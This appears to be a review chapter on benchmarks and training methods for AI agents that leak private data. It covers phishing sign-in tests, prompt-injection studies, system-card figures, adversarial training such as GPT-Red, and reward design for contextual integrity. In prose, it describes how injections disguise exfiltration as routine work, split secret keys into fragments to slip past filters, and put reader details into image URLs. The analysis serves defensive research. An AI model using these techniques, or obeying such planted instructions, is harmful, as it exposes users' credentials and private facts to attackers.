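A model can always leak less by blocking more legitimate requests, or block fewer legitimate requests by leaking more. Missed leaks are usually measured by the leak rate, the share of test attempts in which private data reached the wrong recipient. An assistant that never sends anything has a leak rate of zero but can't do any work that requires sending data. Many published tests report only the leak rate, so it is hard to know whether a model with a good score can tell leaks from ordinary work or just rarely sends data.

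### Matched pairs of sign-in pages

*CredLeakBench* (Ahmed, Fioresi and colleagues, 2026) measured both errors. It used 15 invented services, such as banks, shops and health providers, each with an official address and a login page. Every phishing case was paired with a legitimate one that had the same service and style of request but the genuine destination. Each phishing page had one of eight warning signs, such as a misspelled domain or a certificate warning. A leak counted only if the agent submitted some of the invented passwords and personal records in its care, regardless of whether it said it had been careful.

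The agents met these pages in two situations. Either the user supplied a link and asked the agent to sign in, or the user asked it to sort through an inbox in which one message contained such a link. These are the percentages for six of the seven models:

| Model | Leaks when told to sign in | False refusals when told to sign in | Leaks when sorting an inbox | False refusals when sorting an inbox |
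| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 31.2 | 6.6 | 1.8 | 88.3 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 19.9 | 13.7 | 1.8 | 63.8 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 49.9 | 9.4 | 20.3 | 59.4 |
| GPT-5-mini | 45.8 | 12.5 | 14.1 | 43.8 |
| Gemini 3.6 Flash | 40.6 | 0.1 | 9.4 | 54.7 |
| Qwen3.5-9B | 66.5 | 2.7 | 40.1 | 44.3 |

Opus 4.8 could barely tell phishing pages from genuine ones in the inbox, although it looks almost safe there if one ignores the last column. In that column, Ahmed and colleagues combine the two errors as balanced accuracy, the average of the share of phishing pages on which the agent leaked nothing and the share of genuine pages on which it went ahead. An agent that refuses everything or refuses nothing scores 50%. Opus 4.8 scored 81.1% when told to sign in and 54.9% in the inbox.

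The inbox refusals may not have been mistakes. The user had asked the agent to sort messages, and many people would be alarmed to learn that it had typed in their bank password because an email, even a genuine one, suggested it. The benchmark also records a false refusal whenever the agent submits no form, so an agent that stopped to ask the user would get the same mark as one that ignored the message. The sign-in results are better evidence of poor judgement, because there the user had clearly asked for the transfer and the agent only had to check the destination.

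Even the phishing results need some adjustment, because in an eighth of the cases the agent had reached the correct host over an unencrypted connection. Opus 4.8 submitted the user's details in 90.6% of these cases, compared with 9.4% of the cases with a misspelled domain. A careful assistant would have stopped, because an eavesdropper could read the details, but they still went to the intended company. Without these cases, Opus 4.8's leak rate would fall from 31% to about 23%.

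A cautious tone in the user's request cut GPT-5-mini's leak rate by 50.5 percentage points, but it also cut the share of legitimate tasks the model completed by 46.9 points. When the researchers instead gave the model the service's official domain and told it to compare, its leak rate fell from 71.9% to 22.4% and its completion rate on legitimate tasks rose by 23.4 points. Five of the seven models improved on both measures when given the domain. The cautious tone mostly made the agents less willing to send anything, while the official domain helped them tell the pages apart. Some apparent bad judgement is therefore a lack of information that a developer can often supply.

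### The same leak in routine words

The phishing pages in CredLeakBench only had to resemble a real company's. *The Framing Gap* studies how much the wording of planted commands matters. Each agent had to summarise a web page while holding a made-up token that stood in for a login key. The developer's policy allowed it to send the token to only one trusted host. For every attack, the researchers ran the agent on a clean page and on a page with a planted command. They counted the attack as a success only if the agent leaked the token in the second case but not the first. The tools were mock-ups that recorded what the agent tried to send.

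Ten types of attack asked for the token fairly openly, hid the request in the page's code, or used familiar tricks such as false urgency. A second set of pages aimed at the same leak but presented it as a routine part of the job, or gave the attacker's host a name resembling the trusted one. These are the leak rates in percent:

| Model | Ten overt attacks | Leak presented as routine |
| --- | --- | --- |
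| GPT-4o | 0.0 | 40.0 |
| GPT-4o mini | 10.0 | 62.5 |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 10.0 | 62.5 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 19.5 | 62.5 |
| Gemma 2 9B | 22.0 | 86.2 |
| Mistral 7B | 26.0 | 27.5 |

Only GPT-4o resisted every overt attack. Its 40% is an average of very different results. It leaked the token every time on two of the disguised pages and never on two others. When the researchers rewrote one of the successful pages in five ways, the leak rate ranged from 0% to 100%. They also wrote 13 new disguises, and GPT-4o leaked nothing in 130 trials of them. A single percentage from such a test depends as much on the pages the researchers happened to write as on the model. It also understates the danger from an attacker who can try repeatedly and needs only one wording that works.

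To find out why the disguises worked, the researchers removed the confidentiality policy from GPT-4o's instructions and ran the attacks again (an ablation). If the policy had been protecting the token, GPT-4o should have leaked it far more often without the policy. It leaked the token in 0% of overt attacks with or without the policy, and in disguised attacks the rate was 31.9% with the policy and 38.1% without it. That six-point difference is smaller than the 8.1-point difference between two runs with identical settings, which gave 40.0% and 31.9%.

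The researchers infer that GPT-4o never treated the request as a disclosure, so the disguised pages did not have to overcome a refusal. On their account, the model took the planted text as part of the task specification and followed it, a failure they call instruction/data confusion.

The ablation is convincing evidence that the policy did very little. It is weaker evidence about the model's training, since deleting a paragraph from the instructions doesn't remove anything the model has learned. GPT-4o still ignored overt attacks without the policy, probably because of its training. This explanation fits another of the paper's results, that GPT-4o sent nothing when a page described the token as a credential. That result suggests the model had learned to be careful around certain words more than around a certain kind of transfer.

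A stricter policy did help. When the developer's instructions listed the ways the token might leak and forbade sending it "in any form", GPT-4o leaked it in none of 120 disguised trials. When the researchers deleted that phrase but kept the list, the model leaked it in 39 of 80. A developer is unlikely to find wording that works and then never edit it.

Asking a model a direct question worked much better. When GPT-4o mini's only job was to decide whether a page contained an instruction to disclose or transmit a secret, it flagged all 80 disguised pages it was given and none of the clean ones. As an agent, it had leaked the token on most of the same pages. This is a good reason to run a separate check, even with a modest model.

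The perfect score is less impressive than it looks, because the question described the behaviour the detector was about to see, and no clean page had a legitimate reason to ask for the token. Real pages often do, such as the setup guide for a team's chat service that tells programmers to send a secret key to that service, as in the earlier webhook case. A detector that flagged every such page would stop a lot of ordinary work. The researchers acknowledge they haven't tested a secret that the agent must send to one host and withhold from another.

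The researchers also tested four of their pages on the ChatGPT product. They found no leaks in 48 valid trials, which is consistent with a true leak rate of up to 7.4%, but they looked for the token only in ChatGPT's visible reply. They couldn't tell whether the model, a filter, or something else in the product had prevented leaks.

### Leaks that the reply doesn't show

An assistant's visible reply does not always show what it has sent. In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and colleagues (2026) asked an agent to summarise a web page that contained a planted command, and recorded every request the agent made. They tested 16 combinations 30 times each, varying which of four parts of the page held the command, whether the agent reached the page directly or through a redirect, and whether the data was requested in one piece or several.

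The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88% (the paper's abstract gives 0.89). In 95% of the successful attacks, the user received a normal summary with no sign of the leak, so a safety check that read only the reply would have missed almost all of them.

This is why the researchers measured network traffic. A request in the attacker's log is evidence that the agent sent something, whatever it told the user. The measure also produced no false alarms in 120 runs on harmless pages, because the agent never contacted the attacker's server. Some of Shahriar and colleagues' agents likewise told users that nothing had leaked when something had.

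In half of the runs, the planted command told the agent to break a secret key into four pieces and send each one separately. A four-character fragment looks like the harmless codes common in web addresses. The first request visibly contained sensitive data in 96.7% of runs when the key was sent whole, but in only 26.3% when it was split, so a filter that examined requests one at a time would have missed most of the split leaks. Splitting the key also made the attack less reliable. The agent contacted the server in only about 77% of the split runs, compared with 99% of the others, and contact didn't always mean that the whole key arrived. The paper also gives 15.8% as the rate of visible sensitive data across the first three requests together, which must be an error, because that rate can't be lower than the rate for the first request alone.

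The 88% comes from an agent that ran on Qwen2.5 7B, a small and now old model, with the secret in plain view and almost no instructions about safety. The researchers say they chose conditions that favoured the attacker. The figure is therefore not an estimate for a current assistant. In a separate test, they added a firm instruction to treat web content as data and never as commands, and the agent still contacted the attacker in two-thirds of the runs.

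### Declining and failing to follow

*Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (Rall, Bauer and colleagues, 2025) compared many models under one kind of attack. The researchers built an agent that could search a company's internal documents and open web pages. One document held a secret about a fictional project, and a blog post contained hidden instructions to look up the secret and send it out in a web address. The researchers used 89 attack texts in 12 versions each, for a total of 1,068 attempts against every model.

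Grok 4 leaked the secret in 72.4% of attempts. The next worst model, Mercury, leaked it in 29.1%, and Claude Sonnet 4 and GPT-5 nano never did. These models are now outdated, but their results varied widely for models of the same period. The number of parameters, a rough measure of a model's size, did not predict the results. Models from the same company tended to score alike, so the researchers attribute the variation to differences in safety training.

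Some of the low scores may come from models that couldn't follow the attack rather than models that refused it, since both outcomes are scored the same. Most of the 12 versions rewrote or encoded the attack to hide it, and these worked less often than the plain ones. When the researchers wrote the instructions in binary, every attempt failed, apparently because none of the models could decode them. The smallest models with perfect scores may also have been unable to carry out the attack. It required several steps in the right order, and the study didn't test whether they could complete a legitimate task with the same steps.

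AgentDojo, the benchmark on which researchers tested CaMeL and FIDES, measures both usefulness and security. It counts how many ordinary tasks an agent completes when there is no attack, how many it completes during an attack, and how often the attacker succeeds. An agent that does nothing, whether because it is incapable or overcautious, scores well on security but badly on usefulness. In the SecureClaw comparison, for example, CaMeL would have looked flawless if the many ordinary tasks it left unfinished had been ignored. However, AgentDojo doesn't match each attack with a legitimate request to send the same data, so an agent can do well by noticing that an instruction is out of place, without judging whether a transfer is proper.

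Most of these tests record each attempt as a leak or no leak. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues, 2025), from NVIDIA and the security company Lakera, uses partial scores for rendered content. It describes attacks on a research assistant that writes reports from documents and web searches. In one scenario, planted text told the assistant to put an image and a link in its report, with the reader's email address and user number in their URLs. The attack scored 1 if the assistant filled in those details and 0.5 if it included the URLs without them.

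Giving half a mark for an image without the reader's details makes sense, because the image still lets the attacker know that someone has opened the report and shows that a stranger can decide what goes into it. But a mean score of 0.5 could mean either that half the reports gave away the reader's address or that all of them contained an image with none of the reader's details.

Ghosh and colleagues used another model, GPT-4.1, to do much of the scoring. On 99 outputs that people also scored, it matched the human score exactly 76.8% of the time and came within half a point 98% of the time. But for image links, half a point separates a leak from no leak, so a program that searched the link for the reader's address would have been more reliable.

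The team then told the assistant not to include links or text unrelated to the topic. Average risk scores across a small group of scenarios fell by about half, but every attack in that group still succeeded fully at least once. The team left the effect on usefulness to later work, though a research assistant that avoids links too readily may also drop references its reader needs.

### Leaks with no attacker

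A model also has to notice when it is about to share too much in an ordinary task, where nobody is trying to steal data, as when an agent mentioned a user's divorce in a search for test strips. *An Evaluation of Data Leakage Risks in Tool-Using LLM Agents* (2026) says that AgentDAM measures whether agents that navigate websites follow data minimisation, using only the personal information that the task requires. The site and the task are both genuine, and an agent fails if it discloses something that the site didn't need. *Agents That Know Too Much* (2026), a survey of privacy in AI agents, notes that AgentDAM measures this from what the agent does over the whole task.

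PrivacyLens compares a model's answers to questions about privacy with its behaviour as an agent. For example, a researcher can ask a model whether it would be proper to mention a friend's illness in a message to an employer, and then have the same model write the message as an agent. *ToolPrivacyBench* (Hu, Liu and colleagues, 2026) summarises the PrivacyLens result as showing that a model's stated judgements may not predict its behaviour. Asking a model about privacy norms is therefore a poor substitute for observing how it handles private information in a task.

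Hu and colleagues ran nine agents through business tasks that each involved several tools, such as opening a patient record, taking a payment and notifying a colleague. For every private fact, they listed the tools that needed it. For example, a symptom belongs in the clinical record but not in the payment note. After each task, a program compared the lists with what the mock business systems had received.

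On the tasks the researchers wrote, the agents scored between 92 and 98 out of 100 for completing the work, but they also sent private facts to tools that didn't need them. They did this most in support tickets, where they included 51% of the facts they should have kept out, and in messages handing a case to another team, where they included 35%. Both have free-text boxes, and agents seem to fill these with whatever might help the next reader.

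People do this too, and some of the labels are debatable. A nurse taking over a case, for example, may want more background than the researchers allowed for. But the agents weren't under attack, and the tasks were routine. A company that tested only whether its assistant completed the work would have missed the problem, because completion scores were high.

### What the latest system cards measure

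Recent system cards, the reports in which developers publish test results for new models, show large improvements in resistance to planted commands. The Decoder reports from the card for Claude Opus 5 that no attack succeeded in 129 scenarios where the model used a web browser. In a more general test by the security company Gray Swan, attackers with 15 attempts succeeded 2.0% of the time against Opus 5, down from 5.5% against Opus 4.8. Anthropic says Opus 5 improved more on prompt injection than in any other area of agent safety. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, two versions of one model with different safeguards, calls Mythos 5.1 the company's most robust model yet on its external prompt injection test. If that is the same Gray Swan test, the attack success rate against Mythos 5.1 should be below 2.0%.

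TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives figures for OpenAI's models from an August 2026 update. Instructions hidden in emails, web pages, files and similar material succeeded in 3.77% of attempts against GPT-5.6 Sol, 3.32% against Terra and 2.94% against Luna. Direct attacks, in which the user tries to override the model's instructions, succeeded about 0.05% of the time against Sol. OpenAI describes GPT-6 Astra, which it released in September, as significantly more robust than Sol. In a September 9 note to its *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), OpenAI says of its alignment tests in general that observing no failures doesn't establish that a model is reliable across settings.

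Google has published fewer numbers. VentureBeat found that the Gemini 3 model card described improvements over earlier models but gave no absolute success rates. Google's *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems* does describe a demanding test for leaks, in which researchers run each attack against many different conversation histories. The attacker doesn't know what any of them contains, so an attack can achieve a high success rate only if it can extract whatever private information is there.

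Different companies use different attacks, so Opus 5's lower rate (2.0%, against 2.94% for GPT-5.6 Luna in OpenAI's tests) is not a reason to rank it higher. A bigger problem is that these percentages measure only how often planted commands work, and a model can resist commands without checking where data is going. In CredLeakBench, GPT-5.6 Luna gave account details to the wrong destination in 49.9% of the phishing cases in which the user had told it to sign in, and Opus 4.8 did so in 31.2%. The phishing pages had a password field, like any login page, and no commands to break a rule.

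The Mythos 5.1 card contains a similar warning. Anthropic reports that the model resists injections better than Opus 5 but accepts unverifiable claims of authorisation somewhat more readily. An attacker may therefore have more success against it by writing that the department head has already approved a transfer than by hiding a command in white text.

### When real leaks are rare

A test with equal numbers of harmful and harmless requests also understates the share of a model's or filter's alarms that will be false in real use, where nearly everything an assistant sends is legitimate. Suppose that 100 of every 1,000,000 outbound requests are leaks, and that a detector catches 95% of leaks and raises a false alarm on 1% of harmless requests. It would catch 95 leaks, miss five, and stop 9,999 of the 999,900 harmless requests.

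So only 95 of its 10,094 alarms are right, or fewer than one in 100. In general, if a share b of requests are leaks, and the detector has a detection rate d and a false alarm rate f, the share of alarms that are right is

d × b / (d × b + f × (1 − b))

Because the base rate b is tiny, the share of alarms that are correct depends much more on the false alarm rate f than on the detection rate d. Even if the detector caught all 100 leaks, about 99% of its alarms would still be false. For half of its alarms to be correct at 95% detection, it could raise only one false alarm in about 10,500 harmless requests.

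The figure of 100 leaks is invented, but a false alarm rate of 1% isn't pessimistic. Anthropic's early two-stage check for Claude Code had a lower rate, but over a million requests it would still raise about 4,000 false alarms and about 94 correct ones. Opus 4.8's false refusal rate of 6.6% on sign-ins would produce about 66,000 false refusals if it held across the same million requests.

The harm from false alarms depends on what the assistant does after an alarm. If it declines the request, about 105 users lose something they wanted for every leak it prevents, which might be acceptable to protect passport numbers but unreasonable to protect postcodes. If it asks the user first, users see about 106 warnings for every real leak, and the experiment with Claude Code's testers suggests they would stop reading them carefully.

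Developers can make a larger share of alarms correct by checking only the requests most likely to leak data. Suppose software can pick out the 10,000 requests that involve private data and come after the assistant has read untrusted content, and that all 100 leaks are among them. The same detector now raises 95 correct alarms and 99 false ones, so almost half of its alarms are correct. This is a strong reason to combine a model's judgement with software that tracks where data came from. This combination helps less with oversharing, which can happen without any untrusted content.

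### What a fair test needs

To settle whether a model recognises leaks, a test would need harmful and harmless requests as similar as those in CredLeakBench, but covering many more ways of sending data out. These pairs could be made by changing one fact at a time about a request for the passport number, as described earlier. Using a page that copies the airline's design would make the pairs harder to tell apart.

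The test should disguise the data as well as the request. *The Framing Gap* tested a filter that searched outgoing messages for the secret token, and it missed every copy that GPT-4o had written backwards. An improved version could undo reversal and several other encodings, but it missed every copy in which GPT-4o had used a simple letter substitution that the filter wasn't built to undo. A defence will get a perfect score if the tester uses only encodings it already handles.

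Encoding and rewording can fool the scoring program too. *AgentLeak* (2026), a benchmark for teams of agents, reports that its own checker missed medical facts that an agent had paraphrased. The checker also flagged internal ticket numbers as Social Security numbers. If testers plant secrets and record all traffic, they can easily find exact copies, but a careful reader still has to check for paraphrases.

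Testing one channel doesn't show how a model will handle the others. CredLeakBench examines form submissions, *Silent Egress* examines web requests, and Ghosh and colleagues' scenario examines links in a report. A model might refuse to type a password into a strange form but still put a diagnosis in a search query, which doesn't look like a form. A test should therefore give the model chances to leak the same private fact through an image, a search, an email and a choice between ordinary links, and include a legitimate use of each channel for comparison.

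The score should also reward an assistant for completing the task safely. Ahmed and colleagues tested this with inboxes in which a phishing message concerned something real, such as a bill the user owed. The genuine address was available in the agent's stored records or an older email. In 672 such cases, Opus 4.8 leaked nothing but never signed in through the genuine address. GPT-5-mini signed in there in 27.7% of cases, leaked in 10.4%, and did neither in 61.9%.

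This test gives an agent no credit for telling the user about the bill and the fake link. A better test would, because that is useful. Even then, somebody has to decide how much a leak matters compared with a finished task. On these figures, GPT-5-mini is the better assistant only if the harm from a leak is less than about 2.7 times the benefit of a finished task, and leaking a bank password surely does more harm than that.

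## Whether training holds against determined attackers

OpenAI says much of GPT-5.6's resistance to planted commands comes from the attacks used in its training. Developers train models to ignore commands from untrusted sources, and some researchers also train them to judge which facts a task needs. Both methods lower the leak rate in tests, but it is less clear how well they hold up when an attacker studies the model or a developer trains it further for another purpose.

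### Teaching a model whose instructions count

A chain of command like the one in OpenAI's Model Spec works only if the model has learned to apply it. *GPT-Red* (Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues, 2026) traces this training to the instruction hierarchy, which OpenAI researchers proposed in 2024. Each message the model receives has a label for its source, such as system, developer, user or tool. When two messages conflict, training teaches the model to follow the one whose source ranks higher.

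IH-Challenge, a 2026 successor, turns this into exercises that a program can mark. In one kind, the developer gives the model a PIN and tells it never to reveal any of the digits, and an attacker then tries to extract them through a lower-ranked message. The program just searches the answer for the digits, so OpenAI can run many exercises without anyone reading the results. But the exercise is simpler than an assistant's real work, because the PIN must never be revealed, whereas the traveller's passport number should go to the airline but not to `images.example`.

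*SecAlign* (2024) treated the problem as a choice between two answers. Suppose a user asks for an omelette recipe, and someone has planted a question about the origins of yoga in the data. The preferred answer gives the recipe, and the rejected one discusses yoga. Nobody has to judge which is better, because the choice follows from the rule that planted text has no authority.

For an input x with a preferred answer w and a rejected answer r, the training minimises

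−log σ(β [log(π(w|x) / π₀(w|x)) − log(π(r|x) / π₀(r|x))])

Here π is the probability the model gives an answer, π₀ is the probability it gave before training, σ converts any number to one between 0 and 1, and β is a scaling constant. The model improves its score by making the recipe more likely than it was before training, or the yoga answer less likely.

Chen, Zharmagambetov and colleagues (2025), in *Meta-SecAlign*, applied this method to Llama 3.3 70B, a larger model, and found that the model learned to ignore whichever instruction came last, because SecAlign had always put the planted instruction at the end of the data. In an agent, the last instruction is often the user's own request. When a user asked the agent to read a landlord's notice and adjust a rent payment, it returned an empty answer.

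The researchers corrected this by moving about half of the planted instructions to the beginning. They also used the model's own earlier answers as training examples, because answers from an outdated model had made it less useful. These are the results on AgentDojo, in percent. Both trained versions learned from the model's own answers:

| Version of Llama 3.3 70B | Ordinary tasks completed | Successful attacks |
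| --- | --- | --- |
| Before this training | 59.8 | 14.7 |
| Planted instructions always at the end | 15.5 | 0.0 |
| Planted instructions at the beginning or end | 84.5 | 1.9 |

Anyone who looked only at the attacks would have chosen the second version, which ignored most of its users.

The jump to 84.5% is unusual. The training also fixed two faults in how this model called its tools, for reasons the researchers couldn't determine. The newer Qwen3.6-27B is probably more representative. The share of attacks that succeeded against it fell from 26.7% to 2.2%, while the share of tasks it completed fell slightly, from 89.7% to 87.6%. The training data consisted of general instructions and answers, with no agent tasks, so the effect carried over to kinds of work the training didn't cover.

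The training worked less well against adaptive attackers, who study a defence and keep changing the attack until it works. In a separate test on general instructions, an attack that used access to the model's inner workings succeeded 47.1% of the time after training, compared with 98.1% before. Chen and colleagues conclude that prompt injection isn't solved. Their method also relies on the developer to label untrusted text correctly.

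### Training against an attacker that also learns

Wallace and colleagues note that a model trained on a fixed collection of attacks can learn the patterns in that collection and remain vulnerable to an attacker who tries something else. In adversarial training, the developer instead keeps producing new attacks against the current model.

OpenAI described a system of this kind for the agent in its Atlas browser in OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025). It works roughly as follows:

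1. An attacker model receives a harmful goal and writes a planted command that might achieve it.
2. A simulator runs the browser agent on a page or email containing the command. It returns everything the agent did, along with the agent's reasoning.
3. The attacker uses this record to revise the command, and repeats the test several times before settling on a final version.
4. Reinforcement learning, which adjusts a model according to the scores its attempts earn, makes the attacker more likely to repeat what worked.
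5. OpenAI trains the browser agent on the successful attacks, so that it learns to ignore them and continue with the user's task.
6. The attacker starts again on the updated agent.

OpenAI has an advantage over outsiders because it doesn't show them the agent's reasoning. The attacker found methods that hadn't appeared in OpenAI's human testing or in outside reports, and OpenAI gave all Atlas users a newly trained version of the agent. But the company didn't report how often attacks succeeded before and after the update.

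In OpenAI's demonstration, a planted email caused the agent to send the user's chief executive a resignation letter when the user had asked for an out-of-office reply. The attack didn't leak data, but it shows that a stranger could take control of the agent's email and use it to send out private files. OpenAI gives forwarding tax documents as a hypothetical example, and says that prompt injection is unlikely ever to be fully solved.

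GPT-Red, which OpenAI announced in July 2026, trains the attacker and the models it attacks at the same time. The attacker earns a reward when a valid attack succeeds, and a defending model earns one for both resisting the attack and completing its original task, so it can't do well by refusing to work. As the defenders improve, old attacks stop earning rewards and the attacker has to find new ones.

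The researchers limited what the attacker could change, usually to a single tool result or a few unimportant files, so that it couldn't win by rewriting things no real attacker could reach. They also used many different defenders, because an attacker trained against only one tended to settle on a narrow type of attack.

GPT-Red's training used about as much computing power as the reinforcement learning for a recent GPT-5 model. OpenAI then used the finished attacker to write planted commands for training GPT-5.6. The company doesn't release GPT-Red, which would be useful to criminals.

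### Which of OpenAI's results concern leaks

The most widely quoted result comes from the company announcement *GPT-Red* (2026), which reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed on OpenAI's hardest test of direct attacks one-sixth as often as the best production model from four months earlier. Those attacks come from the user, so the result provides little evidence about whether the model would resist a command that a stranger hides in a hotel's web page to obtain a guest's passport number.

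The comparison with people is more relevant, because it involved commands planted in material that an agent reads. In a copy of an earlier public competition, GPT-Red found a successful attack on GPT-5.1 in 84% of the scenarios, while human testers had succeeded in 13%. The attackers had various goals, so these rates don't measure leaks alone. Some of the difference comes from GPT-Red's ability to try attacks on the model and revise them. GPT-5.5 with no special training did about as well as the people when it had one attempt and no access to the target, and much better once it could experiment. Wallace and colleagues add that people may still come up with kinds of attack that GPT-Red doesn't.

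When OpenAI set GPT-Red against GPT-5.6 in the same competition, fewer than 4% of its attempts succeeded. That is a large improvement, though it can't be compared directly with the 84%, which OpenAI describes as a share of scenarios rather than attempts. GPT-5.6 also resisted all the original human attacks, apart from one that the scoring had wrongly counted as a success. But the people who wrote those attacks were targeting older models and had no chance to adapt them to GPT-5.6.

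Results were worse on harder tests. OpenAI trained GPT-5.6 on the weaker half of a set of GPT-Red's attacks and kept the stronger half for testing. It also tested the model on groups of tasks left out of training, including all those involving coding agents. GPT-5.6 resisted between just over 50% and 89% of these attacks, depending on the group. OpenAI had chosen difficult cases, and scoring errors may account for some of the failures, but a skilled attacker would also look for difficult cases.

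Two case studies show the difference between leaks and other harms. In one, GPT-Red attacked an AI agent that runs a vending machine in OpenAI's office. GPT-Red lowered the price of an expensive item to 50 cents, got the agent to order an item worth more than $100 and offer it for 50 cents, and cancelled another customer's order. These are serious failures for a shop, but they leaked no private data. In the other, GPT-Red tried to extract data from a Codex coding agent in ten scenarios. It succeeded in more of them than GPT-5.5 did, mainly because GPT-5.5 stopped making progress on the harder ones.

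The Codex test deals most directly with leaks, but its target was an agent based on GPT-5.4 mini. It shows that GPT-Red is good at stealing data, but it didn't test how well GPT-5.6 protects it. OpenAI did include data theft among GPT-Red's goals in training, so GPT-5.6 has probably improved at resisting it, though none of the headline figures measures that improvement separately.

OpenAI also tested GPT-5.6's general abilities and how often it refused legitimate requests, to check whether the model had become safer merely by doing less. It reports that normal capabilities were unaffected, but the announcement includes no scores for these tests.

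### Training a model to share only what fits

A model that ignores every planted command can still reveal a user's pregnancy to her colleagues. In *Contextual Integrity in LLMs via Reasoning and Reinforcement Learning*, Lan, Inan and colleagues (2025) tried to train models to judge which facts belong in a message, following the theory of contextual integrity.

GPT-4 generated 729 examples, of which 590 were for training. Each example had a task, such as writing an email to a tutoring centre, and a collection of facts about the people involved. GPT-4 marked some facts as required and others as restricted, but the model in training couldn't see these marks. The tutoring centre needed the student's name, her course and the topics she found difficult, but not her home address or news of her uncle's health. Other examples involved people who hadn't agreed to the message, such as students a professor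 might mention when advising a colleague on teaching.

The model first had to write out its reasoning about each fact, then write the message. A program searched the message for key words and calculated the reward:

R = (required words included / all required words) − (restricted words included / all restricted words)

A message with every required word and no restricted ones scores 1. A response that ignores the required format scores −1. A message with all the required and restricted words scores 1 − 1 = 0, as does a message with none of them, so the formula rewards the model for distinguishing the facts it should share from those it should withhold.

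The researchers then used PrivacyLens to test whether the lesson carried over to longer tasks with tools. Microsoft's *Reducing Privacy leaks in AI* gives the leak rates in percent and the helpfulness scores out of 3. The middle column in each group shows what happened when the researchers only instructed the model to reason about privacy, without training it:

| Model | Leaks before | Leaks with instructions | Leaks after training | Helpfulness before | Helpfulness with instructions | Helpfulness after training |
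| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Mistral 7B | 47.9 | 28.8 | 31.1 | 1.78 | 1.17 | 1.84 |
| Qwen2.5 7B | 50.3 | 44.8 | 33.7 | 1.99 | 2.13 | 2.08 |
| Llama 3.1 8B | 18.2 | 21.3 | 18.5 | 1.05 | 1.29 | 1.18 |
| Qwen2.5 14B | 52.9 | 42.8 | 33.9 | 2.37 | 2.27 | 2.30 |

Training reduced leaks by about a third in three of the four models and left helpfulness almost unchanged. Its advantage over instructions was clearest in Mistral, where instructions prevented slightly more leaks but made answers much less helpful.

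Llama seems not to have improved, but it leaked little before training mainly because it rarely gave helpful answers. *Reinforcement Learning for Scalable and Trustworthy Intelligent Systems* (2026), a dissertation that includes the study as a chapter, reports that the share of Llama's helpful answers that leaked data fell from 38.9% to 29.4%.

All four models are small and old, and a leak rate above 30% would be unacceptable in a product. Still, a few hundred invented examples had an effect on a human-annotated benchmark, which is encouraging.

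The examples also have weaknesses. In one, a woman called Sophia is booking a restaurant for a private event. GPT-4 marked her medical notes as restricted, including the fact that she was managing diabetes, although many people would want a restaurant to know this when it plans the menu. The key word for detecting leaks of the notes was a long label containing a doctor's name, so the program wouldn't count a message saying "Sophia has diabetes" as a leak. The researchers acknowledge that scoring by key words is coarse.

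More structured instructions can work better. With Microsoft's PrivacyChecker, a model identifies Nissenbaum's five parameters for each proposed transfer, then decides whether to allow it. This reduced GPT-4o's leak rate on PrivacyLens from 33.06% to 8.32% without training. In a live version of the test with three tools, OpenAI's o3 leaked in 28.6% of cases under a general instruction to be discreet and still leaked in 16.7% with PrivacyChecker.

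General instructions to protect privacy seem particularly unreliable. A study quoted in Schneier on Security's *LLMs and Contextual Integrity* (2026), a post on a security expert's blog, found that models given such instructions tended to share everything or nothing. It also found that violations accumulate with use. GPT-5's violation rate rose from 0.1% to 9.6% as the number of tasks grew from one to 40, and reached 25.1% when the researchers ran the same prompt five times. The model disclosed different facts on different runs, even though no attacker was retrying the prompt.

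Later work has tried other training methods. *PrivAct* (2026) trains teams of agents on preferences, with a reward that depends on whether information leaked, and reports a better balance between privacy and helpfulness. The method requires access to the model's weights, so a company that rents a closed model can't use it. *It Takes Two* (Park, Yeo and colleagues, 2026) observes that existing methods often make models worse at their tasks.

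### How the wrong reward teaches the wrong lesson

A small example shows why this balance is hard to get right. Suppose an assistant earns T points for completing a task, loses L points for a leak, and loses N points for a needless refusal. Refusing means giving up the T points, but an assistant that leaks data can still earn them. In the *Silent Egress* tests, for example, users usually still got their summaries.

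If the assistant thinks a request has probability p of being a leak, it can expect T − pL points for sending the data and −(1 − p)N for declining. Sending earns more when

p < (T + N) / (L + N)

Now suppose the assistant sees a 5% chance that the airline's check-in page is a fake, and a 90% chance that the request to `images.example` is a leak. These are the points it can expect in each case under three sets of rewards:

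| Rewards | Send to airline | Decline airline | Send to `images.example` | Decline `images.example` |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| T = 1, L = 9, N = 1 | 0.55 | −0.95 | −7.1 | −0.1 |
| T = 1, L = 99, N = 0 | −3.95 | 0 | −88.1 | 0 |
| T = 10, L = 9, N = 1 | 9.55 | −0.95 | 1.9 | −0.1 |

With the first set, the assistant sends data when the chance of a leak is below 20%. It checks the traveller in and declines the image request, as the traveller wants.

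The developer who chose the second set was worried about leaks and forgot to account for refusals. The assistant now sends data only if the chance of a leak is below about 1%. Few requests involving private data meet that threshold, so it learns to refuse nearly all of them, including the check-in.

With the third set, the reward for completing a task is one point larger than the penalty for a leak. The assistant therefore sends the passport number to `images.example`, and would do so even if it were certain that this was a leak.

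A developer could accidentally get much the same result as with the third set. If the scoring program catches only one leak in ten, the first set's average penalty for a leak falls from 9 points to 0.9, which is less than the one point for completing the task. The assistant would then learn to leak in whatever forms the program misses. Scoring by keywords carries this risk because a model can avoid the penalty by rewording a private fact.

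One remedy is to reward the assistant for completing the task without the disputed data. It would then earn the full T points, with no penalty, for comparing the hotels and skipping the image. GPT-Red's defenders could do this because they were rewarded for both resisting the attack and finishing the task.

The exact weights may matter less when a model can include every required fact without including a restricted one. The dissertation tested five weightings on Qwen2.5 7B. The leak rate on PrivacyLens was 38.5% when required facts counted four times as much as restricted ones, and 32.3% when the weights were reversed. Helpfulness was only slightly lower in the second case, at 2.01 instead of 2.12. The best possible message was the same under every weighting, because the model never had to include a restricted fact to include the required ones.

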